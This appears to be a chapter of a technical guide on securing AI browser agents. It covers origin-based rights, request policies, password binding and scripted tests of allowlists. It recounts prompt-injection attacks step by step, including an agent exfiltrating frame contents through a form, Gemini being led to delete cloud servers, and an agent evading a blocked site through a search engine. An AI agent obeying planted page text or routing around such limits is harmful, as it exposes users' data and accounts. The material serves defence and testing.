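Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, tested seven agentic browsers by hand in late January and early February 2026. They set up pages on two domains, each with a different fact about an imaginary Alice. On one page she liked cats, and in a frame inside that page she liked horses. They asked each agent which animals Alice likes. If the answer included horses, the agent had read the frame.

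The researchers used other pages to test whether the agent would read a second tab, type into a form, or read a password that the browser displayed as dots. They counted a behaviour as present after one success and repeated failed attempts at least three times in new chats. They tested ChatGPT Atlas with and without Agent Mode.

| Agent | Reads a frame from another site | Reads a tab from another site | Types into a page at the user's request |
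|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT Atlas, Agent Mode | Yes | No | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | With permission | Yes, in Auto Browse mode |
| Claude for Chrome | Yes | With permission | Yes |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | No | Yes, except passwords |
| ChatGPT Atlas, ordinary mode | No | Through chat memory | Asks to switch to Agent Mode |
| Microsoft Edge with Copilot | No | Yes | No |
| Brave Leo | No | With permission | No |
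| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No |

The agents in the first four rows could both read across sites and type, which is enough for an attack if an injection succeeds. A "no" in the table is weaker evidence than a "yes" because it can mean either that the agent lacks the ability or that the model declined, and the tests didn't always show which.

On Atlas in Agent Mode, the researchers carried out the full attack on their own test pages:

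1. They opened a page that contained a form and a frame from a second site.
2. They asked the agent to summarise the page.
3. Text on the page told the agent to include the frame's contents and enter the summary into the form.
4. The agent did this, and the form submitted itself to the first page's server.

The attack also worked in reverse, with a hostile frame taking text from the page around it. This is more worrying because sites usually don't show private data in frames on other sites, but a page with private data may well contain an advertisement.

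The study used a simplified injection. The same basic test failed on Claude for Chrome, Comet and Gemini, whose models refused to follow instructions found in a page. The study therefore shows what these browsers allow once an injection succeeds, not how often one does.

OpenAI declined the report because it didn't include an end-to-end injection attack. Brave, Google and Microsoft sent responses that the researchers call thoughtful. The University of Washington, where both researchers work, later reported that Perplexity had also declined and that Anthropic and Firefox had not responded. OpenAI has since announced that it is retiring Atlas, according to SC Media's *Agentic anarchy*. The researchers' findings are still relevant to the other three browsers that met the conditions.

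Roesner and Kohlbrenner also describe how false information can cross between sites without any injection. Atlas, Gemini and Comet used earlier conversations when they answered questions about Alice. If a user once asked about a phishing page that gave a false telephone number for their bank, the agent might later repeat that number as the bank's own. Similarly, the purchasing agent could reuse a false price weeks after the operator removed its source from the allowlist. Each task should therefore start with an empty memory.

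### Separate rights to read and to act

Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026) recommends extending the same-origin policy to agents. Wang and colleagues did this in BrowserOS, an open-source agentic browser, and report that their mechanism kept the browser useful and slowed it only slightly.

Google has published a design for Chrome that gives the agent different rights on different origins. Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, describes two sets that the browser keeps for each session. The agent may read pages from read-only origins. On read-writable origins it may also click and type. The design works like this:

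1. The planner, the model that reads pages and chooses actions, proposes the origins it wants to use.
2. A separate gating function decides which of them are relevant to the user's task. It receives no untrusted web content, so a planted review can't influence it directly.
3. Chrome withholds everything else from the model. If a page contains an advertisement in a frame from an unlisted origin, the model never receives the advertisement's text.
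4. When the planner wants to visit a new origin, another model checks its relevance before Chrome adds the origin and starts the navigation. The same check applies if a page moves to a new origin by itself.
5. The user can share further pages with the agent. The planner may use their content, but it still can't add an origin without approval.

A second model, the User Alignment Critic, reviews every action the planner proposes. It receives only metadata about the action and rejects any action that doesn't serve the user's goal.

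If the purchasing agent used this design to file a receipt, shop.example would be read-only and docs.example writable. The agent could copy the receipt to docs.example but couldn't paste a contract into a form on shop.example. Chrome also limits model-generated URLs to known public ones, much as OpenAI's link check does.

Chrome's first version was simpler than the design and tracked only the read-writable set. That may be why Roesner and Kohlbrenner found Gemini reading frames from other sites about two months later. They also say it isn't clear how Chrome determines relevance or how well that judgement resists malicious input. Parker gives no error rates. With a handwritten allowlist, nobody can extend the agent's access during a task, so an operator whose agent does the same job every week gains little by letting a model choose the origins.

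At the Black Hat security conference in August 2026, researchers from the company Zenity demonstrated attacks on five AI browsers. SC Media reports that Chrome did best. The researchers struggled to make Gemini open a malicious URL and succeeded only by having it assemble one from pieces. They also got Gemini to delete virtual servers at Amazon Web Services. Google patched all the flaws that Zenity reported. An origin set can't prevent such a deletion if the task has made the site writable, so the operator also needs a way to permit some actions on a site and refuse others.

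### Rights to individual actions

Rules that limit what an agent can do on a site are hard to write for clicks, because a click at the same position can open an email or delete it, depending on the page. An agent can also get around rules for navigate commands. In *ceLLMate*, Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025) barred Browser Use from navigating to Hacker News, but the agent searched for the site on DuckDuckGo and clicked the result.

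Their system, ceLLMate, applies its rules to the HTTP requests that clicks and key presses produce. A request that places an order looks the same to the rule whichever button caused it. On Amazon, the system would work as follows:

1. The site's developers publish an "agent sitemap", a file that gives a name to each kind of request that matters for security. A GET request for the basket page is `ViewCart`, and a POST request to the checkout address is `PlaceOrder`.
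2. The developers or another trusted party write policies that allow an action, deny it, or allow it under a condition, such as a total of no more than a set amount.
3. The user gives the agent a task. A language model reads only the task and the policy descriptions, predicts which sites the agent needs, and picks the smallest sufficient set of policies. It also fills in values such as a limit of $50.
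4. The user reviews the selection and confirms it. After that, nothing on a web page can change it.
5. A Chrome extension intercepts each request and looks up the decision. It refuses requests to unrelated domains.

Conditions such as a spending limit take extra work to enforce. Amazon's order request doesn't include the total, so the extension copies the amount from the checkout page and keeps it until the request goes out. A limit of $50 per order would still let the agent check out two baskets of $49, so the system can also count orders and permit only one.

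Meng and colleagues tested how well models chose policies on 209 tasks from shopping, travel and software sites. The models chose exactly the right set in 94 to 100 per cent of tasks, depending on the model and the kind of site. They did worse when they also had to fill in values, getting 81 to 97 per cent of 32 shopping tasks right. One model mistook a wishlist for a shopping basket and granted permission to add goods to the basket. The user has to catch errors like that during the review in step 4.

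To test enforcement, the researchers assumed that an attacker completely controlled the agent. They wrote 12 scripts that attempted harmful actions on GitLab, such as deleting a project or adding an attacker's access key, while the policies allowed only reading and writing issues. The extension blocked all 12. Every attack needed an action that the policies didn't allow, so the result confirms that the enforcement works but provides little evidence about attacks that use permitted actions. The system doesn't examine the contents of permitted comments.

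A series of 11 page visits took 13.93 seconds without the extension. With the extension, it took 14.94 seconds with 100 sitemap entries (about 7 per cent longer) and 16.02 seconds with 300 (about 15 per cent longer). The delay matters little for an agent that spends most of its time waiting for the model.

Adoption is the larger obstacle. The researchers wrote their GitLab sitemap by hand, and it covers 51 kinds of request. If a site's sitemap omits an action, the approach adds no protection for that action. Roesner and Kohlbrenner object that the approach burdens web developers and depends on correct policies. The approach also leaves out WebSockets, whose messages often use site-specific formats.

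### Writing rules for the purchasing agent

The company has three fixed tasks, so a person can define the agent's rights once. The company doesn't need a model to select those rights, and it doesn't have to wait for shop.example to publish a sitemap.

| Task | On shop.example | On docs.example |
|---|---|---|
| Find a product | Open product pages | Nothing |
| Place the order | Change the basket and place one order | Nothing |
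| File the receipt | Open the order page | Upload to the receipts folder |

The operator performs each task with a test account while the interceptor records the requests, then names the ones the task needs. The code below uses `permittedUrl` from earlier sections and `rights`, the set of actions for the current task.

```js
const names = {
  "GET https://shop.example/basket": "view basket",
  "POST https://shop.example/basket": "change basket",
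  "POST https://shop.example/orders": "place order"
};
function permittedAction(request, rights) {
  const href = permittedUrl(request.url, entries);
  if (!href) return false;
  const url = new URL(href);
  const key = `${request.method} ${url.origin}${url.pathname}`;
  return rights.has(names[key]);
}
```

The function blocks any request without a name, including one that changes the delivery address. The interceptor applies the function to page loads and background requests, while a separate list covers images and scripts. Product pages have too many URLs to name individually, so the finding task can use the set of known URLs from the exact-URL rule instead.

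Some sites send all their background requests to a single address and put the action in the request body. On these sites, the function also has to read the body, and the operator has to repeat the recording whenever the site changes.

### Binding passwords to sites and separating profiles

Binding each password to a site prevents leaks like the one Mudryi and colleagues demonstrated, in which the Browser Use library typed a password into a hostile form. An older version of Browser Use's cloud service let the operator store each secret under a URL pattern, such as `https://admin.example.com`. The library can then check the current page against the pattern before typing, and leave the field empty on any other site, such as `other.test`.

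These patterns need the same care as allowlist entries. A password stored under `https://*.shop.example` can also be used on the shop's forum, and a pattern that begins with `http*` also covers unencrypted pages.

The protection ends once the password is in the field. In the Washington tests, Claude for Chrome and Atlas in Agent Mode could read passwords that the page displayed as dots. A library should omit the contents of password fields from the page text it gives the model. According to Parker, Chrome does not give the model access to stored passwords and asks the user before its password manager signs in to a site.

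Separate browser profiles limit the data an agent can carry between sites. The company can use one profile logged in only to shop.example and another logged in only to docs.example, so the contracts are behind a login page while the agent is shopping. Ordinary code moves the receipt from one task to the next, so no model has text from both accounts in its context at once.

Neither profile should have access to a mailbox. SC Media reports that Zenity's researchers got the Claude extension to log in to accounts protected by a second factor. The extension waited for the one-time codes to arrive by email.

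Separate profiles can still share conversation history. Most of the agents that Roesner and Kohlbrenner tested save conversations to the user's account with the vendor, so the operator also needs to use separate vendor accounts or turn off the agent's memory.

### Asking a person before consequential actions

Chrome's agent has a fixed list of sensitive sites, such as those for banking or medical information, and asks the user before opening one. It also tries to pause before purchases, payments and messages. According to Parker, these pauses rely partly on models to recognise consequential actions, so the agent can miss some.

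The main objection, as with link warnings, is that people stop reading prompts that appear often. Roesner and Kohlbrenner cite usability studies in which users didn't reliably notice or act on warnings, and frequent requests for permission led to less secure behaviour. In one of their own tests, a frame contained instructions for Claude for Chrome. The agent asked whether to follow them, and only after a "Yes" altered the page around the frame, which belonged to another site.

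This is a good argument for asking rarely. The rules above already block actions the agent never needs, and opening a product page doesn't need approval, so the agent only has to ask once per order. If the company buys paper every two weeks, someone will see about 26 prompts a year and can reasonably read each one.

The confirmation prompt should show the items, the total and the delivery address. Ordinary code should take these details from the checkout page, because a model that has followed a planted instruction may also write a misleading summary. The prompt should appear outside the web page, where the site can't imitate or cover it, and the agent must not be able to press the confirmation button.

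### Pages that change between the check and the action

A person may approve an order at $500, and the price may rise before the agent clicks. The same problem can occur without an approval step, because the page can change during the seconds the model takes to choose an action. Programmers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use flaw.

Jiang, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Atomicity for Agents*, define it precisely. Let Bind(a, s) be the element or value that action a refers to when the page is in state s. If s₁ is the state that the agent observed and s₂ the state when it acts, the flaw occurs when

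Bind(a, s₁) ≠ Bind(a, s₂).

The researchers built nine test scenarios and added five real websites. In some scenarios, a subscription window or advertisement appeared where the agent was about to click. In others, a price rose from $500 to $700 although the user had set a limit of $600, or a one-time password expired before the agent could submit it. None of this requires prompt injection. On the Forbes home page, the agent can accidentally click an ordinary advertisement that loads late.

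All ten open-source agents tested failed in at least one of these three ways, and most failed in all three. Agents that click at screen coordinates were vulnerable to moving elements. Agents that select an element through the page's structure often avoided that problem, because the action fails if the element is gone. But they still bought at the wrong price, because the button stayed the same and only the number beside it changed.

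An allowlist stops a misplaced click if the advertisement leads to other.test. It does nothing about a changed price on shop.example.

The proposed fix adds a check just before each action:

1. When the library captures the page, it attaches two monitors that browsers already provide. One records changes to the page's elements, text and important attributes, and the other records changes in the size of visible elements.
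2. The monitors keep recording while the model chooses an action.
3. Immediately before the action, the library looks at the records. If they are empty, it goes ahead.
4. If anything has changed, it cancels the action and alerts the user.

Jiang and colleagues report that this substantially reduces unintended actions and shortens the vulnerable period from seconds to about a tenth of a second, which is the delay between the final check and the click. They note that code outside the browser can't remove this remaining delay because it has no standard way to freeze a page.

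The fix can produce too many alerts on a busy page, because a rotating banner or a stock counter also counts as a change. If each change triggers an alert, the user will go back to dismissing prompts. A library could instead capture the page again and let the model choose again, alerting the user only after several failures. The monitors also cover only frames from the page's own origin, so they wouldn't record a change inside a payment form loaded from pay.example.

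The interceptor can pause the request that places an order and, if the request contains the total, compare the total with the amount the person approved. If the shop leaves the total out of the request, as Amazon does, a payment card with a low spending limit is a simple safeguard, because the card issuer applies the limit when the shop charges the card.

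## Testing whether a restriction holds

A broken restriction usually looks the same as a working one until something tries to open an unlisted host. The purchasing agent orders its paper either way. The operator therefore has to try opening unlisted hosts deliberately, with a test account and invented data, before giving the agent a real login.

### Testing without the model first

Suppose the operator tells the agent to open other.test, and the model declines because the page has nothing to do with buying paper. The library never received a navigate command, so the refusal doesn't show whether the agent has a working allowlist.

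The first tests should replace the model with a script that returns prepared commands, such as "open this URL" or "click this button", in the format the library expects. The library runs the same checks on these commands as on the model's. A second script can send commands straight to the browser's debugging port, which bypasses the library's check and tests the layers behind it.

The tests need two web servers on domains the operator owns. The operator temporarily adds the first, start.test, to the allowlist and uses it to serve pages with redirects, forms, frames and pop-ups, because the operator can't add these to shop.example. The second, other.test, stays off the allowlist and records everything it receives.

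The browser must be able to reach other.test if the restriction is missing, so the server needs a public address, a valid certificate and port 443. The purchasing agent's proxy refuses private addresses and other ports regardless of the allowlist, so a test server on the office network would receive nothing even if someone had added its name to the list by mistake.

Before relying on a clean result, the operator should run a positive control by adding other.test to every list, running the tests and confirming that each request arrives. Kaur (2026), in *What AI Red-Team Evaluations Can and Cannot Prove*, asks for the same in tests of models, because finding no failures means little if the procedure can't detect one. *Systematic reviews of adverse effects*, a guide for medical researchers, likewise tells readers of a study that reports no side effects to ask how thoroughly the researchers looked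 for them.

A test without a control can pass without testing anything. GitHub's *Domain & Network Integration Test Analysis* (2026) reviews 56 tests of the company's firewall for agents. One is named for blocking a specific domain but only confirms that a subdomain of a permitted domain loads. Another, meant to test browser access to a local server, starts no server and only prints text. The analysis found no test in which a permitted site redirects to an internal address.

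### Three possible outcomes

A test passes if the forbidden server receives nothing. The agent's summary and the library's log are not reliable evidence, because the summary can look harmless after a leak and the log can record a page as blocked after the request was sent.

Each test should use its own code in the URL, so that the operator can match requests to tests, and its own random word on the page. This small Node.js server records the requests and returns the words:

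```js
https.createServer(certificate, (request, response) => {
  const test = request.url.split("/")[1];
  console.log(new Date().toISOString(), test, request.method, request.url);
  response.writeHead(200, {
    "Content-Type": "text/html", "Cache-Control": "no-store"
  });
  response.end(`<p>${words[test]}</p>`);
}).listen(443);
```

The `no-store` header tells the browser not to save a copy of the page, which it could later show without contacting the server. After each test, the operator searches the saved prompts for the word. If the library sends screenshots to the model, someone has to check those for the word too.

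| Outcome | Evidence | Which aims fail |
|---|---|---|
| Nothing sent | No request in the server's log | None |
| Request sent, page withheld | Request in the log, but the word is not in any prompt | Keeping data private; protecting internal services |
| Page read | The word is in a prompt | Both of these, and keeping hostile text from the model |

AWS publishes a sample check for Nova Act, its toolkit for browser agents. The check would probably stop an agent that had been redirected to a site outside the allowlist, but the request to that site may already have gone out, because the check examines the URL that the browser is already on. If the check can't find a host name, it correctly refuses to continue.

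The operator should record DNS lookups and bare connections separately, because some layers allow them by design. GitHub's firewall allows lookups even when its list is empty, and the analysis found no test for data hidden in them. The purchasing agent's proxy refuses requests for an unlisted host before looking it up, so a request for other.test should produce neither a lookup nor a connection.

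### The test matrix

The table gives the expected results for the purchasing agent's setup. Every category also needs a successful request to start.test, because a browser with no connection would pass the other tests.

| Category | What the script tries | Expected result | Layer responsible |
|---|---|---|---|
| Host comparison | URLs with a permitted name outside the host; hosts that only resemble a permitted one | Nothing sent | Library check, with the browser policy and proxy behind it |
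| Redirect hops | Redirects from start.test that end on other.test, or pass through it and return | Nothing sent | Interceptor and browser policy, then proxy |
| Interactions | A click, key press, form, pop-up and delayed script that lead to other.test | Nothing sent | Interceptor and browser policy, then proxy |
| Frames and subresources | A frame, image, script, background request and WebSocket from other.test | Nothing sent | Browser policy for frames; interceptor and proxy for the rest |
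| Internal addresses | A test service on the browser's machine; another on the office network, by address and through a permitted name | Neither service receives anything | Interceptor for addresses; proxy and firewall for the permitted name |
| Empty list | Starting the agent with the list missing, then empty | The agent doesn't start | Startup script |
| Failure of the checker | A forbidden request after the interceptor, the library check or the proxy has stopped, and after a browser crash | Nothing sent; with the proxy off, start.test doesn't load either | The layers still running |

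The expected result of a test depends on the product. If a page in a Browserbase session loads an image from other.test, the allowlist is working as documented, because it covers only the main page. For an operator who wants to keep data private, the test has still failed, and the operator needs another layer of protection.

agent-browser's *Security*, which documents a command-line browser tool for agents, describes much wider coverage: page loads, subresources, WebSockets and other background connections. However, the tool blocks WebSockets by replacing part of the browser's JavaScript inside the page. The documentation warns that page scripts could in theory restore the original if the agent has permission to run its own JavaScript. The WebSocket test should therefore use the same permissions as the real agent.

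The documentation is also a good source of tests for the last two categories. According to it, the tool rejects an empty allowlist, saves the list with the session, reapplies it after a crash, and does not start if the saved file is damaged. An operator can check each claim in a few minutes.

Most scripted tests give the same result every time, so two or three repetitions are enough. Tests that depend on timing need more repetitions. OpenClaw, for example, intercepts page loads only for a limited time after an action, so a test script should try to open other.test immediately, after a second, after ten seconds and after a minute.

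Once all the tests pass, the operator should switch off one layer at a time and run them again. Otherwise, the tests can pass because the proxy works, even if the interceptor never attached to the browser.

### Reading a partial failure

The numbers in this example are illustrative. The operator has set up the purchasing agent and runs 42 scripted tests.

| Category | Tests | Nothing sent | Request sent, page withheld | Page read |
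|---|---|---|---|---|
| Host comparison | 8 | 8 | 0 | 0 |
| Redirect hops | 6 | 6 | 0 | 0 |
| Interactions | 10 | 9 | 1 | 0 |
| Frames and subresources | 8 | 7 | 1 | 0 |
| Internal addresses | 4 | 4 | 0 | 0 |
| Empty list | 2 | 2 | 0 | 0 |
| Failure of the checker | 4 | 3 | 0 | 1 |

The three failures were the first request of a pop-up, a WebSocket, and a frame that loaded after the script had stopped the interceptor. They seem unrelated, and extending the interceptor to pop-ups would fix only the first.

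But the proxy should have refused all three requests, and its log contains no refusals. It has no entries for start.test either, though pages from start.test loaded throughout the run, including in the test with the proxy switched off. The operator had counted that test as a pass because other.test received no requests.

The browser was therefore not using the proxy. Its `chrome://policy` page was empty because the agent library had started its own build of Chromium, which doesn't read Chrome's policy directory. The firewall should have blocked the direct connections, but its rule covered only IPv4, and both test servers also have IPv6 addresses.

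So the interceptor had stopped most of the requests, and the outer layers had contributed little. The operator moves the policy file, adds IPv6 to the firewall rule and reruns all 42 tests, because the 39 passes came from the old setup.

### Testing with the model

Scripted tests cover only the routes the operator thought of. A model may find others, as the agent in the ceLLMate study did when it reached a forbidden site through a search engine. It may also respond badly to a refusal, for example by placing an order twice.

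To test a restriction, the operator can copy a product page to start.test and add a review telling customers to go to other.test. The agent gets an invented delivery address and an ordinary request to buy paper, and each run starts in a new session. The operator separately counts the runs in which the model tried to open other.test and the runs in which that site's server received anything.

Suppose, again with illustrative numbers, that the model tries to send a request in 12 of 100 runs and the server receives nothing. The allowlist has then stopped only 12 requests. The other 88 runs show how often the model resisted this particular review, but they don't test the allowlist.

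A single run isn't enough, because the same model can respond differently to the same page. The US government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation tried five attacks on a 2024 model in *Strengthening AI Agent Hijacking Evaluations*. The average success rate rose from 57 per cent with one attempt at each attack to 80 per cent with 25. Newer models resist much better, but repetition still helps the attacker. Schneier on Security's *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) reports success rates against Claude Opus 5 of 0.2 per cent on one attempt and 2.0 per cent within 15.

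A test that repeats the same text also underestimates how often an attacker who can revise it would succeed. *BrowseSafe++* (2026) tested seven agents on 1,024 tasks. The original injections succeeded on 0.49 to 4.00 per cent of tasks, depending on the agent. When the researchers adapted them over up to 64 attempts, the rates rose to 30.66 to 95.41 per cent. An operator should therefore vary the planted review and, if possible, have someone rewrite it after seeing how the agent responds.

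### What zero failures show

Suppose the model never tries to open other.test in 100 runs. If p is its true rate of trying and the runs are independent, the chance of seeing no attempts in n runs is (1 − p)ⁿ. The upper 95 per cent bound is the value of p at which this chance falls to 5 per cent:

(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, so p ≈ −ln(0.05) / n ≈ 3 / n.

By the rule of three, which works well for more than about 30 runs, the upper bound on the rate of attempts after 100 runs without one is about 3 per cent. The company orders paper about 26 times a year. If the agent met such a review every time and tried to follow it in 3 per cent of cases, the chance of at least one attempt in a year would be 1 − 0.97²⁶, or about 55 per cent.

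Reducing the upper bound takes many more trials. Kaur calculates that an evaluator needs 299 trials without a failure to get it below 1 per cent and 2,995 to get it below 0.1 per cent. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports no successful attacks on Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios. If each scenario counts as one independent trial, the true rate could still be as high as 2.3 per cent.

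Runs often aren't independent. If the operator tests ten reviews ten times each, the runs with the same review will tend to agree, so 100 runs contain less information than 100 different reviews would. Kaur gives a standard correction for groups of m runs with correlation ρ:

effective number of runs = n / [1 + (m − 1)ρ].

With m = 10 and ρ = 0.1, the 100 runs count as about 53 independent runs, and the bound rises to roughly 5.7 per cent. Kaur treats this as an approximation and recommends a statistical model of the groups for formal reporting.

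When an attacker revises a text after each attempt, the attempts are also dependent, so Kaur counts the whole series as one trial, even if it contains 100 attempts. Anthropic's browser tests gave an adaptive attacker 100 attempts per environment. With improved safeguards, 1.4 per cent of attacks on Claude Opus 4.5 succeeded, but the chance that at least one of an attacker's 100 attempts succeeds could be much higher.

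The bound also applies only to the conditions of the test. VentureBeat reports that attacks on Claude Opus 4.6 failed in all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment. In a graphical interface without safeguards, 17.8 per cent of attacks succeeded on the first attempt and 78.6 per cent by the 200th. Similarly, an agent's resistance to instructions planted in reviews is weak evidence that it will resist instructions in a PDF or a chat message.

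*Building Browser Agents* (2025) argues that even minimal failure rates are unacceptable for agents with access to email, banking or company software. Few operators can run enough model tests to show that an agent's failure rate is low enough. They can instead make sure that any attempt to reach a domain outside the allowlist fails, which the scripted tests check.

### Testing again after changes

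The tests that Browser Use publishes for its allowlist are a good model for checking upgrades. Each test runs the URL check on an allowlist and a URL, with an expected result of permit or refuse. The cases include permitted names in the userinfo, similar-looking domains, wildcard entries, wrong schemes and the browser's own settings pages. They also include URLs that must remain permitted, because a check that refused every URL would pass if the tests only covered URLs it should refuse.

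The notes to pirate's fix for the userinfo flaw include the command for running these tests, so an operator can rerun them after each upgrade and add tests for the entries on the company's own allowlist. One test expects the check to accept userinfo. An operator who refuses all userinfo, as recommended earlier, has to change that test to expect a refusal.

These tests don't open any pages, so they run quickly but can't show whether the library runs the check after a click or a redirect. An upgrade can break that behavior while every URL test still passes, so the operator should repeat the server tests too.

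The tests should run after any change to the agent library, the browser, the proxy or the list. A hosted browser can change without any action by the customer, so it makes sense to test one weekly. Browserbase, for example, warns that its experimental allowlist may behave differently in future releases. The agent's startup script can also try one forbidden request through each layer and exit if other.test receives anything.

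### What to log and when to raise an alarm

For each refused request, the log should contain the time, session, host and port, the layer that refused it, the agent's last command and the page that was open. Full URLs may contain the private data that the refusal protected, so they belong in a separate log that few people can read. Browser Use's `record_har_path` setting saves a trace of the browser's network traffic. The trace includes response content by default, so it needs the same protection.

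The outer layers need their own logs, stored where the agent can't change them. GitHub's firewall records all network activity, and AWS can report its firewall's actions as metrics that trigger alarms.

For the purchasing agent, these events deserve different responses:

- If the library refuses a navigate command, the task should pause and someone should read the log that day.
- If the proxy refuses a page that the library or the interceptor should have refused first, an inner check has failed. The operator should stop the agent until the cause is clear, even though nothing got out.
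- If the agent is running but the proxy's log is empty, the browser may have found another route.
- If a request has reached an unlisted host or an internal service, the operator should treat it as a security incident.

### What to do when a forbidden request appears

1. Stop the agent and disconnect the browser's machine from the network. Keep the machine, its browser profile and the saved prompts, because restarting with a fresh profile would destroy the evidence.

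2. Work out which of the three outcomes occurred by comparing the logs. The operator usually can't see an outside server's log, so a connection that the proxy allowed counts as a request sent.

3. If the request went out, assume that the recipient has everything in its URL, headers and body. Change any exposed passwords, revoke access tokens and end the logged-in sessions on the sites themselves, since deleting the browser's cookies doesn't end a session that someone else has copied. If the request reached an internal service, check what it changed there.

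4. Find the text that caused the request. In the running example, this might be a review on shop.example, which the company should report to the shop. Check the order history and the sharing settings on docs.example for the same session, because a misled agent may also have acted on permitted sites. Earlier sessions that loaded the same review need the same check.

5. Add a test that reproduces the route. Confirm that it fails with the old configuration and passes with the new one, then run the full matrix before the agent gets its login back.
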